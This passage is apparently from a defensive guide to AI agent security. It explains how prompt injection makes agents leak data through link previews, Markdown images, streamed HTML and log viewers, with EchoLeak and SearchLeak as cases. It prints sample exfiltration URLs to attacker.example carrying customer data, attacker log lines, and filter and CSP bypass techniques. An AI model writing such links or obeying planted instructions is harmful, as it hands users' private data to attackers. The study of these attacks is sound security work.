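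Even a check on the right person can fail if the text changes afterwards. RyotaK described an attack in which the attacker waits for a trusted user to open an issue mentioning `@claude`, then edits the issue before the agent reads it. Anthropic responded by ignoring issues and comments edited after the trigger. In August 2026 the security company CodeAnt AI reported a related flaw in workflows that start when someone adds a label. The workflow checked the permissions of the person who triggered the run, but set the cut-off for new comments at the latest use of the same label, possibly by someone else. Adding the label again could therefore let in comments posted after the check.

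### Agents that keep answering each other

Two agents that respond to each other's posts can keep going without an attacker. A single agent can also answer itself. Mercer, in *Claude Code Keeps Replying to Its Own PR Comments?*, describes an open problem in which Claude Code's pull-request monitor treats its own replies as new feedback. The suggested workaround is for the agent to ignore any comment that ends with its automated-reply marker, though it still receives each comment first.

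In *Agents of Chaos* (2026), 20 AI researchers spent two weeks trying to break agents on a shared Discord server and by email. They tested loops deliberately, in one attempt by setting up two agents to relay each other's messages. The exchange went on for more than a week, but a user kept prompting the agents during that time, so the test doesn't show that they would have continued that long unaided.

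Agent frameworks usually limit the number of steps in a run. *When Agents Do Not Stop* (2026) cites `max_iterations` in LangChain and `max_turns` in OpenAI's Agents SDK, and argues that a limit helps only if it covers the path that feeds results back to the agent. A loop through a chat channel can avoid these limits because each reply may start a new run with its counter at zero. An agent limited to ten steps per run could therefore post one short answer per run indefinitely.

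Platform limits can catch what the agent's own counter misses. GitHub's *Rate Limiting Controls*, a document for its AI-driven workflows, describes a workflow that starts three agents, each of which starts three more, so that the fifth round would produce 243 new agents. GitHub therefore lets each run assign work to only one agent by default, and waits ten seconds between assignments if a developer raises the limit. It can also restrict how often a user starts workflows, but by default this limit exempts accounts with write access, which would include the support agent's account.

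Letting each run start only one agent prevents exponential growth, but the chain can still continue forever if each agent starts another. GitHub's 20-minute limit on an agent's work doesn't end the chain, because it applies to each run separately. A developer can set a `stop-after` deadline, after which the workflow no longer runs the agent.

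## Link previews that contact an attacker's server

A chat platform can leak an agent's data through link previews, even if no other bot reads the channel. To build a preview, the platform's crawler requests each posted address exactly as it appears in the message. If an attacker has steered the agent into posting an address that points to the attacker's server and contains private data, the crawler sends that data to the server before anyone clicks the link.

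Even some specialists were slow to notice this. Rehberger returned to the problem in 2024 with a post about Slack apps. In a short note on that post, *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, Willison (2024) wrote that he had not thought of this way of stealing data before.

### From a hostile ticket to a log entry

A web address can carry data in its query string, the part after a question mark, which websites use for things like search terms. The server receives the whole query string with the request, and most web servers log every requested address. An attacker therefore needs only a domain name and an ordinary server to collect data sent this way.

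Suppose the software company's support agent posts its summaries to a private Slack channel.

1. An attacker sends a ticket about failed exports. Further down, the ticket asks for a "diagnostic link" in any summary, ending with the email address and plan of the last customer whose record the agent opened.
2. The agent reads the ticket, and the model follows the request as if it came from the support team.
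3. The model fills in the link. It replaces spaces with plus signs and the at sign with the code `%40`, because an address can't contain spaces and some characters have special meanings:

```
https://attacker.example/diag?d=ana.ruiz%40customer.example+enterprise+plan
```

4. The integration posts the summary, including the link, to the private channel.
5. Slack's crawler requests the address, and the attacker's server adds a line to its log:

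```
203.0.113.7 [05/Mar/2026:10:14:32] "GET /diag?d=ana.ruiz%40customer.example+enterprise+plan" 404 "Slackbot-LinkExpanding 1.0"
```

The line begins with the IP address of Slack's server (a placeholder here) and the time. The code 404 after the requested address means that the attacker's server has no such page, but the attack still works because the data arrived with the request. The line ends with the name the crawler sends to identify itself. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* shows that name in a real log entry, recorded after Rehberger posted a link to Slack through a webhook.

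Servers and browsers usually accept URLs of a couple of thousand characters, which is plenty for a password or an access key. An attacker who wanted a whole customer list would need many links, and somebody in the channel would probably notice them.

A single link is easier to overlook. Slack lets a program display a label, such as "diagnostic report", in place of the address, and it still generates a preview for most labelled links. Embrace The Red mentions that the data in the address can also be hidden with ASCII smuggling, which encodes text in characters that most programs don't display. A colleague who spots the link and deletes the message is too late, because the attacker already has the log entry.

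Preview requests can also cause trouble without an attacker, when the agent posts a link by mistake. If it posts a customer's single-use login link, the crawler may use it up before the customer can log in. If it posts a private link to a contract, the platform's server may download a copy of the contract.

### Who makes the request

In the example, the platform's server makes the request, but in some chat apps the sender's or recipient's device makes it. *Link Previews* (2020), by Talal Haj Bakry and Tommy Mysk, compared popular apps on iPhones and Android phones. The table shows their findings and what each design reveals to whoever runs the linked server, in addition to any data in the address.

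| Who fetches the page | Apps in 2020 | IP address revealed | Time revealed |
| - | - | - | - |
| Platform's server | Slack, Discord, Zoom, LinkedIn, Twitter, Facebook Messenger, Instagram, Google Hangouts, LINE | The platform's | Roughly when someone posted the link |
| Sender's device | iMessage, WhatsApp, Viber, Signal with previews on | The sender's | Roughly when the sender wrote it |
| Each recipient's device | Two apps that the study left unnamed | Each recipient's | When each recipient saw the message |
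| Nobody | Threema, TikTok, WeChat, Signal with previews off | None | None |

Link previews expose the most when each recipient's app fetches them. The app contacts the linked server as soon as the message appears on the screen, and the recipient's IP address can reveal their approximate location. Someone who posted a link to their own server in a channel with 200 members could learn when each member saw the message and roughly where they were. Mysk reported the problem to both companies. One had fixed it by the time the study appeared, and the other was still working on it.

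When the platform's server fetches a preview, it normally hides the readers' IP addresses from the linked site. LINE's server was an exception because it passed on the IP addresses of both sender and recipient, which the company stopped after receiving the report. Hiding the readers doesn't prevent the theft of customer data, because the attacker gets that data from the query string, which is the same whichever computer sends it.

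Fetching by the sender assumes that people trust the links they send. That is reasonable for a person, but an agent under an attacker's influence will send a link that nobody at the company chose. When an agent posts, the sender's device is the computer that runs the integration. That computer contacts the attacker's server if the integration generates previews as a phone app would, but there may be no preview request if the integration sends only text. The same agent can therefore leak data through one app and not through another.

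Some platforms also limit how much a crawler downloads. In 2020 the limit was 15 MB at Discord and 50 MB at Slack, while Facebook's servers had none for files sent through Instagram. These limits protect the platform's capacity and the privacy of linked documents. They don't prevent exfiltration, because the crawler sends the private data in its request, before the download begins.

The number of requests in a log doesn't reliably show how many people saw a link. When the researchers sent a 2.6 GB file through Instagram, several Facebook servers fetched it at once and downloaded about 24.7 GB in total. Caching can reduce the number of requests. Slack told Mysk that it keeps previews for about 30 minutes, so if two people post the same address within that time, the second post may not cause a new request.

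A cache gives little protection against theft because it only prevents repeat requests for an address the platform has already fetched. The first time the agent posts an address containing a customer's email, the crawler has to request it. Posting another customer's data creates a new address, so the crawler makes another request.

Some details of the 2020 results are out of date. Facebook, for instance, switched off previews in Messenger and Instagram for European users in early 2021 because of European regulations. Slack's basic design is the same. According to its current documentation, *Unfurling links in messages*, Slack's servers have to fetch every address in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to before they decide whether to show a preview. A link may therefore have leaked its data even if it appears in the channel without a preview.

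### The Slack MCP server

The best-documented flaw of this type was in a connector that Anthropic wrote for Slack. The connector used the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way for AI applications to use outside tools. Each tool comes with a small program, called an MCP server, that carries out the model's requests. When Anthropic introduced the protocol, it published several example servers on GitHub, including the Slack connector, which could read and post messages.

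An operator could restrict this MCP server to a single private Slack channel, but an agent allowed to post there could still send data outside the company. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* explains that the restriction controls where a message appears, but Slack's crawler will still follow a link in it to any server on the internet. The MCP server did not turn previews off, so letting the agent post without approval risked more than a strange message in front of colleagues, even though outsiders could not read the channel.

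In the first of Rehberger's two demonstrations, a developer asked Claude Code to analyse a source file that contained instructions in characters that people can't see but the model can read. Claude Code opened the developer's `.env` file, where programmers often keep passwords and keys, and posted to Slack a link that included an API key. An API key lets whoever holds it use a service in its owner's name.

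The second demonstration used Claude Desktop, Anthropic's app for general users. The user asked it to summarise a document and post the summary for the team. The document contained an instruction to add a link containing the latest message from another Slack channel, called "matrix". The model did so, and the message appeared in the log of Rehberger's server.

One posted link could leak the data several times. If the link pointed to an image, Slack sent requests from three crawlers, which appear in the log as Slack-LinkExpanding, Slackbot and Slack-ImgProxy. The extra requests are mostly redundant for an attacker, but they mean that a company blocking only one crawler by name would not stop the leak.

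Most AI applications ask the user to approve each tool call, which gives the user a chance to notice the link. Embrace The Red predicts that many users will turn these requests off as they come to trust the model. The restriction to one private channel would make turning them off easier to justify.

Rehberger reported the flaw to Anthropic on 27 May 2025. Two days later, Anthropic archived the server, leaving the code online but no longer maintaining it. It is unclear whether the report prompted this. Anthropic had no plan to fix security flaws in its archived servers and agreed that Rehberger could publish the details.

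The server's package had more than 14,000 downloads a week at the time, and Embrace The Red inferred that there might be tens of thousands of vulnerable installations. That is possible, but downloads are a rough measure because automated systems often download the same package again for every test run, and some people install a tool and never use it. An installation is also exposed only if its agent has private data and reads text that an attacker can influence. *Anthropic Slack MCP Server Data Exfiltration via Link Unfurling*, an advisory from the vulnerability-tracking company VulnCheck, lists all default deployments as affected.

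The repair takes two lines, which an operator has to add to the functions for posting messages and for replying:

```
unfurl_links: false,
unfurl_media: false,
```

When Rehberger tested the server with these lines added, Slack no longer generated previews. Anyone who still runs the original code has to make the change themselves. Embrace The Red suggests using a server made by the vendor of the product it connects to, since a vendor is more likely to keep releasing security fixes.

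Ratings of the flaw's severity differ. VulnCheck scored it 9.3 out of 10, or "critical", and the US government's vulnerability database lists that score in NVD's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025). The government's own analysts have not added a score. Rehberger rated the flaw 7.5, or "high". He also asked several chatbots for a score, and the three that answered gave 8.7, 9.1 and 9.3.

Much of the difference between the two scores depends on which kinds of damage are counted. VulnCheck's score assumes that the attack can severely compromise confidentiality and also severely alter and disrupt other systems, but the demonstrations showed only data theft. A stolen key might let an attacker cause the other damage, depending on what it gives access to. Rehberger gave no breakdown of his figure, but it matches the score that an older version of the scoring system gives to an equally exploitable flaw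 that only exposes data. Data exposure alone seems the better description of the flaw itself.

VulnCheck also assumed that the attack needs no action from a user, which is true when an agent posts without supervision. If a person has to approve each message, the attack depends on that person missing the link. Neither score measures how much is at stake in a particular installation, which depends on what the agent can read. That may be only public documentation, or, on a developer's laptop, it may include the keys to a company's servers.

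It is still common to assume that permission to post is low-risk. Kemple's *Data & security best practices for agentic Slack apps*, published on Slack's developer blog in April 2026, recommends that companies always allow `chat:write`, the permission to post, as low-risk, and require approval for permissions that read channel history or user details. It does not cover link previews. Posting is low-risk for a bot that sends fixed messages, but an agent that handles private data can leak that data by posting.

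### PromptArmor's public test

The flaw in the Slack MCP server, a single product, gives little indication of how many other agents have the same problem. In February 2026 the security company PromptArmor tried to find out with a public test, and its *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes how the test worked.

The company set up a website, AITextRisk.com, that recorded every preview request it received. Participants used their own agents in their usual messaging apps. If an agent's message contained a link to the site and the app fetched the link, the request appeared in a public log with the data in the address. One published entry included a name and an API key.

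The log usually showed which app had made a preview request, because crawlers such as Slackbot send their names, but not which agent had written the link. Participants added this information by "claiming" a log entry and stating which agent they had used. They could also report an agent that had produced no preview request. PromptArmor used these reports to chart the riskiest combinations of agent and app, and those that appeared safe.

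OpenClaw on Telegram and some Slack bots were among the combinations that leaked data. OpenClaw is an agent that people run on their own computers and instruct through a messaging app, and its default Telegram settings allowed previews. Its replies may go to a private chat with its owner, but that gives no more protection than the private Slack channel did. Apostol, in *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, also names Microsoft Teams with agents built with Microsoft's Copilot Studio as a combination that leaked.

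OpenClaw on Telegram also provides the clearest example of a setup that did not leak. When its owner switched link previews off, the test site received no data. Comparing the same setup with previews on and off is more informative than comparing different products, because only one setting changes.

A claimed log entry is fairly good evidence that a combination can leak, but it is not proof. Slack's crawler sends the same request whether an agent or a person posted the link, and a participant could have named the wrong agent. Several independent reports about the same combination would make such an error unlikely.

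Reports that nothing happened are much weaker evidence. The agent may have refused to write the link, or left out the `https://` that Slack requires before it generates a preview. The participant may have disabled previews earlier and forgotten. Agents also receive frequent updates, so a combination that was safe for one person in February might leak for someone else with a different version or settings.

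The test also can't show how common the problem is. Participants chose to take part, and nobody counted the people who tried an agent and reported nothing. If Teams appears often in the log, that may only be because many participants use it. The site also measured only the last step of the attack. It didn't test whether an outsider could have steered each agent into writing the link, and models differ in how easily they follow planted text.

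### Preview switches and their defaults

Each Slack message has two preview settings, which the program posting it can control. `unfurl_links` covers pages that are mostly text, and `unfurl_media` covers images, video and audio. To prevent a leak, a developer has to set both to false.

| `unfurl_links` | `unfurl_media` | Text page | Image or video | Does Slack fetch the address? |
| - | - | - | - | - |
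| left out | left out | documentation disagrees | preview | yes |
| `false` | left out | no preview | preview | yes |
| left out | `false` | documentation disagrees | no preview | yes |
| `false` | `false` | no preview | no preview | no |

Slack has to fetch a link to find out whether it leads to text or media, so it still contacts the server when only one setting is off, as the second and third rows show. A developer who sets `unfurl_links` to false and tests with a news article will see no preview and may wrongly conclude that Slack no longer contacts the server.

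Slack's documentation is inconsistent about whether links to text pages get previews by default. The preview guide and the reference for posting messages both state that Slack unfurls all links from users and apps. Yet the same reference describes `unfurl_links` as a way to enable previews of text, which would be unnecessary if they were already on. An example in the preview guide also shows a text link that gets no preview until the developer sets `unfurl_links` to true. The default affects how a channel looks, but an attacker gets the data whether or not a preview appears.

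The preview guide now advises developers to consider disabling previews for messages from a language model, but developers who start elsewhere may miss this. Slack's *Developing an agent* explains how to build an agent's replies, and its sample request for posting a message sets neither switch, so an agent built from that sample will have previews on. *Developing an agent* also covers streaming, in which a reply appears piece by piece through a different set of requests. Slack's instructions for the switches refer to posted messages and webhooks, so a developer who streams replies should test the switches separately.

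Telegram's bot API has a similar option. A bot can turn previews off by setting `is_disabled` to true in `link_preview_options`, but they are on by default. OpenClaw users have a simpler way to turn them off. According to PromptArmor, they need to add `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram section of the agent's configuration file, `openclaw.json`. Without that line, the agent was exposed in February 2026.

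Discord also shows link previews, which it calls embeds, by default. A program can hide all of a message's embeds by setting the `SUPPRESS_EMBEDS` flag, and anyone can hide the embed for a single link by putting the address in angle brackets. Hiding an embed may not stop Discord's crawler from contacting the linked server, so developers should check this before relying on either method for security.

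A developer can test a defence against link previews by posting a link to a server they control, with a made-up word in the query string, and looking for that word in the server's log. They should use a new word for each attempt, because a cached preview could make a failed defence appear to work. They should also test both an image link and a text link through every function the agent uses to post.

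The switches apply to one message at a time, so a developer can easily forget to set them on some messages. The fix to Anthropic's server had to cover replies as well as new posts. Sending every message through one function that always turns previews off is safer, much as a bot-wide default protects against unwanted mentions on Discord.

Slack's other ways of suppressing previews are unreliable defences. Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* explains how users can hide previews in their own app. This probably changes only their own view, since the server fetches the page for the whole channel. Slack also shows no previews if a message contains more than five links, but the attacker decides how many links to ask for. Nor does it show a preview if a link's label is just part of the address. In the last two cases, Slack promises only that no preview will appear, not that it won't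 fetch the address.

If a team turns previews off, links still work and readers lose only a title and a picture. Embrace The Red suggests leaving previews off by default for any AI system that posts to a messaging app, and proposes a list of permitted domains for teams that want to keep some previews.

Turning off link previews does not remove the hostile link from the support agent's message. The data stays in the channel until someone clicks the link, which sends the same request that the preview crawler would have sent. Because the theft now depends on a colleague clicking, it is less certain, and the team has time to find the message. Turning off previews also has no effect on other programs that load addresses automatically, such as AI chat windows that display images.

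### Who should turn previews off

PromptArmor says messaging platforms should give developers control over link previews, and people who build agents should use that control or pass the choice on to their users. It would also like platforms to offer the setting for individual chats and channels, so that a company could create a channel where an agent's links are safe regardless of which software posts them. Apostol summarises the argument as placing most of the responsibility on the platforms, but PromptArmor's own text divides it more evenly.

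The Slack case shows that giving developers control over previews is not enough. Anthropic's server posted with previews on, even though Slack already had both switches when the server went into use and Rehberger had published the two-line fix in August 2024. Each developer has to learn about the problem separately, and an abandoned program keeps its old settings.

A platform could protect all of them by changing the default. Slack already labels some apps as agents, so it could turn previews off for those accounts and let developers turn them back on. That change would miss agents that post through a webhook or an ordinary bot account, as the support agent may well do. Turning previews off for every bot would cover those agents, but would also remove the pictures and headlines from news feeds and other bots that have never used a language model.

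The agent's developer is the right person to decide when a link preview is worth the risk, because the developer knows whether the agent handles private data and reads text from strangers, which the platform can't see. A channel setting like the one PromptArmor proposes would help with agents whose developers never made that decision, because a company's administrator could apply it without changing the agent's code.

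## Images in AI chat windows that leak data

An agent's answer can leak data even if nobody posts it to a chat platform. The chat windows where people read a model's answers, on web pages or in apps, often display images. If an attacker has steered the model into writing an image address that contains private data, the reader's browser sends that data to the attacker's server when it displays the answer.

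### From Markdown to a web request

Language models usually format their answers in Markdown, which uses ordinary characters to mark formatting, such as two asterisks on each side of a word for bold type. To include an image, the model writes an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets and the image's address in round brackets.

Suppose the software company also has an internal web page where staff can ask the support agent about tickets. An attacker's ticket asks for a "status icon" at the end of any answer, with the details of the last customer in its address. An employee asks for a summary of the ticket, and the model ends its answer with this line:

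```
![status](https://attacker.example/icon.png?d=ana.ruiz%40customer.example+enterprise+plan)
```

The chat window converts the Markdown into HTML:

```
<img alt="status" src="https://attacker.example/icon.png?d=ana.ruiz%40customer.example+enterprise+plan">
```

An image tag contains only the address of a picture, so the browser must request the file to show it. It normally does this as soon as it reads the tag, because people expect pictures to appear without a click. The attacker then finds the customer's details in the server's log, as with a link preview.

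Unlike a link-preview crawler, the reader's browser requests the image when the text appears on the screen, so Slack's link-preview settings would not protect the company's web page. Only the developer of the chat window can decide whether it loads images, and from which addresses. The same answer can leak its data again if a colleague later opens it in another program. The attacker also learns the reader's IP address unless another server relays the request.

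### The first findings and their fixes

Researchers found this problem in two of the best-known chatbots in the spring of 2023. Roman Samoilenko demonstrated it on ChatGPT with a single-pixel image, too small for a reader to notice. Samoilenko's web page added the instructions to any text a visitor copied, as Willison described in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (2023). The visitor then unknowingly pasted the instructions into ChatGPT along with the text.

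Bing Chat, Microsoft's chatbot, could read the web page a user had open, so an attacker could plant instructions in a comment or advertisement on that page. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes a test in which the instructions told the model to wait two turns, then assemble an image address from separate pieces and add a short summary of the page and the conversation, along with any passwords it could see. Rehberger reported the problem on 8 April 2023, and Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had fixed the flaw.

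His old attacks no longer worked, and he noticed that Bing Chat now had a content security policy (CSP), a header that restricts the addresses a web page can load content from. The policy allowed images from only four Bing addresses.

OpenAI took longer. Rehberger had reported the same flaw in ChatGPT in early April 2023, but his attack still worked in a live demonstration that December. The next day he found a new check, which Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes. Before the ChatGPT web page displayed an image, it sent the image's address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe` and loaded the image only if the service classified the address as safe.

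OpenAI didn't publish the rules behind the check, and the results looked arbitrary. Rehberger put 36 images on his server, one for each letter and digit, and ChatGPT loaded nine of them. Each of the nine could leak one character, and he used two of them to send the word "hi" to his server. The method is slow, and OpenAI could notice it in its logs, but passwords are short and Rehberger expected the method to improve.

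Because ChatGPT's web page itself called the service, every other version needed its own copy of the check. Rehberger notes that the iPhone app didn't have one in December 2023, and neither did the macOS app that OpenAI released the following year. The image flaw had exposed one conversation at a time, but by then ChatGPT could store facts about a user in a long-term memory and read them in later conversations. Rehberger showed that a malicious web page or document could write an instruction into this memory, after which ChatGPT quietly sent him everything the user discussed.

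The web version had gaps too. According to Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, the check trusted `windows.net`, a Microsoft domain where anyone can rent storage space and read a log of the requests it receives. An attacker could therefore collect data there. Rehberger had reported some of these gaps in October 2024 and found them still unfixed in 2025. The security company Tenable also got past the check that year.

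Many other products had the same flaw. Rehberger lists eleven in which he found it, including Anthropic's Claude, Google's Bard and NotebookLM, and GitHub Copilot Chat. Willison (2024) adds Writer.com and Amazon Q, and explains that GitHub fixed Copilot Chat by stopping it from showing images from untrusted domains. Most of the large vendors made similar fixes, but xAI closed Rehberger's reports about Grok as "Informational", according to Willison's *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"*.

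New products still have this flaw. In 2026 the security company Rapid7 reported that the macOS app for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, automatically loaded images from any address the model wrote. An attacker could have used this to steal source code and API keys, though nobody is known to have done so. OpenAI had dealt with this type of leak in ChatGPT more than two years earlier, and has since published a more thorough protection against leaks through web addresses. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* warns that some of OpenAI's own developers may not know about that protection, which may explain the flaw in the Codex app.

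### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their emails, files and Teams chats. It had several defences against image leaks, but in January 2025 the company Aim Security told Microsoft how to get past all of them. Aim Security named the attack EchoLeak, and the flaw is registered as CVE-2025-32711. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) gives the original account.

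The attacker only had to send the victim an email. When an employee asks a question, Copilot searches the employee's data for relevant passages and gives them to the model with the question. The attacker can't know what the employee will ask, so Aim Security wrote a long email with headings for many topics, such as staff onboarding and leaves of absence, and repeated the same instructions under each. If an employee asked about leave, Copilot would then probably retrieve part of the email.

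The instructions told the model to put the most sensitive information it could see into a web address. The attack had to bypass four defences to trigger a request to that address.

**The injection classifier.** Microsoft used a classifier meant to detect prompt injections in incoming text and keep them from reaching the model. Aim Security worded its emailed instructions as if they were for the recipient, without mentioning Copilot or AI, and the classifier let the email through. Business emails often contain requests, and a request to a colleague can look the same as a request to a model.

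**The link filter.** Copilot removed links to outside websites from its answers, but the filter recognised only the usual Markdown notation, with the address in round brackets directly after the label. Markdown also has a reference style, which puts the address on a separate line:

```
[project status][ref]

[ref]: https://attacker.example/?d=SECRET
```

The filter did not remove this version, and the chat window displayed it as a working link. At this stage, the attack worked if the employee clicked the link.

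Copilot also removed ordinary Markdown images, but this filter had the same gap, so adding an exclamation mark in front of the first line was enough to get an image into the answer. The browser would then request the image's address automatically.

The browser still blocked the image, because the content security policy (CSP) on Copilot's page allowed images only from about 30 addresses and patterns, most of them Microsoft's. Aim Security searched this list for a server that would fetch another address on request.

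SharePoint, Microsoft's service for internal websites, had one, but it worked only if the victim accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Microsoft Teams had a preview service without that restriction. The final image address had this form, with a placeholder for the Teams server:

```
[ref]: https://teams-preview.example/content?url=https://attacker.example/SECRET
```

The browser requested a Teams address, which the CSP permitted. The Teams server then requested the address at the end of that Teams address, which sent the secret to the attacker. A CSP controls only what the browser loads, so it had no effect on the Teams server's request.

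Copilot normally names the sources of an answer, which could have led the employee to the strange email. The attacker therefore told the email's "recipient" never to refer to it, citing compliance reasons. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, write that the victim would have seen nothing more suspicious than a broken image or link.

Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, a month before the details became public, and said no customers had been affected. According to Reddy and Gujral, Copilot now removes reference-style links and embedded images from outside content. That would be a weak fix on its own, because an email can describe an image without containing one. In 2023, Rehberger's instructions for Bing Chat used this approach by having the model assemble the image from pieces.

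Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click attack on a major AI application. That is fair if "zero-click" excludes attacks in which the user must first open a malicious page or document with the chatbot. The method of leaking data was familiar, and Willison described EchoLeak as an extended version of attacks that researchers had already shown on about a dozen products. Aim Security added evidence that several defences used together could all fail, each for a separate reason.

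Reddy and Gujral also assess which defences would have stopped the attack, using public accounts rather than experiments. They expect a strict CSP, a list of permitted addresses, human review and an image proxy (a server that fetches pictures on readers' behalf) to prevent the automatic leak. Copilot already had a CSP, so "strict" must mean that no server the policy allows will fetch an address chosen by the attacker.

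Their paper contradicts itself about another defence, keeping strangers' emails out of answers to internal questions. The text says this would make EchoLeak fail "by design", but the table marks it as unable to stop the leak. The text seems right, since the model would never have read the attacker's instructions.

### SearchLeak and filters that act too late

A year after EchoLeak, researchers at the security company Varonis stole data from another part of Microsoft 365 Copilot, Copilot Enterprise Search, which finds information in a company's emails, meetings and files (*SearchLeak*, 2026). Microsoft's filter for dangerous HTML worked correctly on finished answers, but the attack succeeded because the browser loaded the image before the answer was finished.

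AI chat windows usually display an answer while the model is still writing it. Copilot's filter put the model's HTML inside a code block, which makes a browser show tags as plain text, but it did so only once the answer was complete. Until then, the browser treated the tags as real HTML.

The attack went as follows:

1. The attacker sends the victim a link to Copilot's search page on Microsoft's own domain. The address contains a search query, and Copilot follows the query as an instruction.
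2. The victim clicks. The query tells Copilot to find an email, take its title and put the title into the address of an image.
3. Copilot begins to stream its answer, which includes the image tag.
4. The browser requests the image at once. The address belongs to Bing's image search, which the page's CSP allows.
5. Bing's server fetches the picture that it is supposed to search for. The picture's address is on the attacker's server and contains the email's title.
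6. Copilot finishes, and the filter turns the tag into harmless text.

Varonis shows the resulting entry in the attacker's log:

```
GET /Your_Security_Code_847291/img.png
```

A stolen email title can expose a login code, since many services put these codes in the subject line. Varonis warns that an attacker could also have taken the text of emails, meeting details and confidential files, since Copilot can read whatever its user can. This follows from how the attack worked, although the instructions Varonis published extract only a title.

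Unlike EchoLeak, SearchLeak required the victim to click a link, but the attacker didn't have to rely on Copilot retrieving a particular email. The link led to a real Microsoft address, so software that blocks suspicious links was unlikely to stop it.

Microsoft registered the flaw as CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June 2026, according to The Next Web, and had fixed it by the time Varonis published its report on 15 June. Microsoft rated the flaw "critical" on its own scale but gave it 6.5 on the standard 10-point scale. *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (The Hacker News, 2026) reported that the US government's vulnerability database gave it 7.5.

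The danger of streaming was publicly known by then. GitLab, a code-hosting service similar to GitHub, has an assistant called Duo, which displayed its answers line by line. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, from May 2025, explains that the page could treat a tag as working HTML because it didn't yet have the rest of the answer.

GitLab Duo passed its answers through DOMPurify, a widely used HTML sanitiser that removes scripts but by default permits image tags, which are harmless on most web pages. Legit Security hid instructions in a public project, and when a user asked Duo about a file there, Duo put code from the user's private project into an image address. GitLab then stopped Duo from displaying images and forms that point to outside domains.

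Varonis recommends that developers sanitise text at the moment a page displays it, not afterwards. For a streamed answer, the chat window has to check each piece before the browser displays it. It also has to hold back an unfinished tag until the rest arrives, since half an image tag may look harmless. A simpler solution is to stream plain text and add the formatting at the end, after the filter has run. Readers can still follow the answer as the model writes it.

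A filter can also run in time but check for too few kinds of content. In autumn 2025 Rehberger noticed that Microsoft 365 Copilot could show a preview of HTML that the model had written. The preview removed image tags but kept instructions to load background pictures or fonts through the style sheet, the part of a web page that sets its appearance.

Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes an attack that leaked an email through a font address. A user opened a malicious shared Word document and typed "hi there" to Copilot. Instructions in the document made Copilot find an email with a secret code and write a page whose font address contained the email's text. Copilot normally showed such pages as code, which would not have loaded the font, so the instructions also told it to show the preview. When it did, the browser requested the font, which sent the email's text to the server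 at that address.

Rehberger had first tried background images, but the CSP restricted their sources, and the restrictions varied between Word, Excel and the other programs that contain Copilot. The rules for fonts were looser. Microsoft received his report in October 2025 and finished fixing the flaw, CVE-2026-24299, on 5 March 2026. Allowing only a short list of harmless tags would have blocked the font, whereas a filter that removes known dangers has to cover every way a page can load a file.

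### Logs and messages that someone opens later

Blocking every image in a chat window protects only the people who read the answer there. Companies also store their agents' answers, and other programs may display them later.

PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes such a leak in the website where OpenAI's customers manage their applications. Developers can read logs there of past conversations between their application and its users. The log viewer formatted the model's answers as Markdown and loaded the images in them.

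To demonstrate the problem, PromptArmor built a mock application that helps a bank check a new customer's identity. The application combined six sources, including the customer's documents and material from the internet in which PromptArmor had planted instructions. When the bank's employee asked a question, the model wrote an image address containing the customer's personal and financial data. A second model that checked each answer blocked the image, so no data leaked.

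The block also marked the conversation for review. A developer opened it in OpenAI's log viewer to see what had gone wrong, and the developer's browser loaded the image. The attacker's server received the customer's passport details and credit history from an answer that the bank's employee had never seen.

An application's defences can thus make the later leak more likely, because developers tend to read the conversations that filters flag. A user's complaint can have the same effect. In an example from PromptArmor, a filter removed an image from an answer by the search service Perplexity, leaving the answer strangely empty. A user might well click "thumbs down" on such an answer, and a developer investigating the complaint would open the original text.

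PromptArmor found the same behaviour in several of OpenAI's tools for building and testing agents. It warned that the flaw exposed all applications built on the affected services, which is true in the sense that none of those applications could prevent it. To steal data, an attacker would still have had to get instructions into an application's data, and somebody would have had to open the affected conversation. The attacker can't control when that happens, but can wait for it.

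Such a report can easily fail to reach the vendor, as happened with OpenAI. PromptArmor submitted it on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that sorts vulnerability reports for OpenAI. After three rounds of questions, Bugcrowd closed it on 4 December as not applicable. OpenAI learned of the flaw only when PromptArmor published its findings. On 22 January 2026, OpenAI reopened the report and said it was working on a fix.

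Logs need to contain the model's exact output, because developers can't investigate an attack if a filter has deleted the evidence. The safest solution is therefore to store the original output and display it as plain text in the log viewer. The browser then doesn't request the image, and developers see `![status](https://attacker.example/...)`, which is more informative than a broken picture.

An agent can also cause a delayed leak by sending a message. Copilot Cowork is a Microsoft agent that carries out tasks with a user's emails, chats and files. According to Microsoft's documentation, it asks for permission before sending an email or posting in Teams. But PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* reports that it does not ask when it sends messages to its own user.

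A message can leak data even if no outsider receives it. In PromptArmor's test, the user had added a file of instructions from the internet to help the agent write weekly reviews. Five of its 81 lines came from the attacker and described a service that supposedly creates previews of documents. Copilot Cowork collected download links for the user's files, put them into image addresses and sent the user a Teams message with the images. When the user opened the message, Teams loaded the images, which sent the links to the attacker. Anyone with such a link can download the file without logging in.

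The attack worked in all five trials, including with Claude Opus 4.7, one of the most capable models available at the time. Five trials with one set of instructions can't give a general success rate, but they show the result was not a fluke. The user's view of the agent's work never showed the message's content, so watching the agent would not have helped.

PromptArmor treats the problem as a consequence of the product's design and suggests that administrators block downloads from sensitive SharePoint sites. That would make the stolen links useless, but it would also prevent employees from opening files from those sites in Word or Excel, a serious drawback for many companies.

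The software company has to consider this risk everywhere its support agent's text may appear. Its internal web page may block outside images, but a weekly email report, an archive of old tickets or an error log viewer may display the same summary and load the images. Each of these programs needs its own protection, and somebody has to remember to protect any new ones the company adds.

### Disagreements over what counts as a flaw

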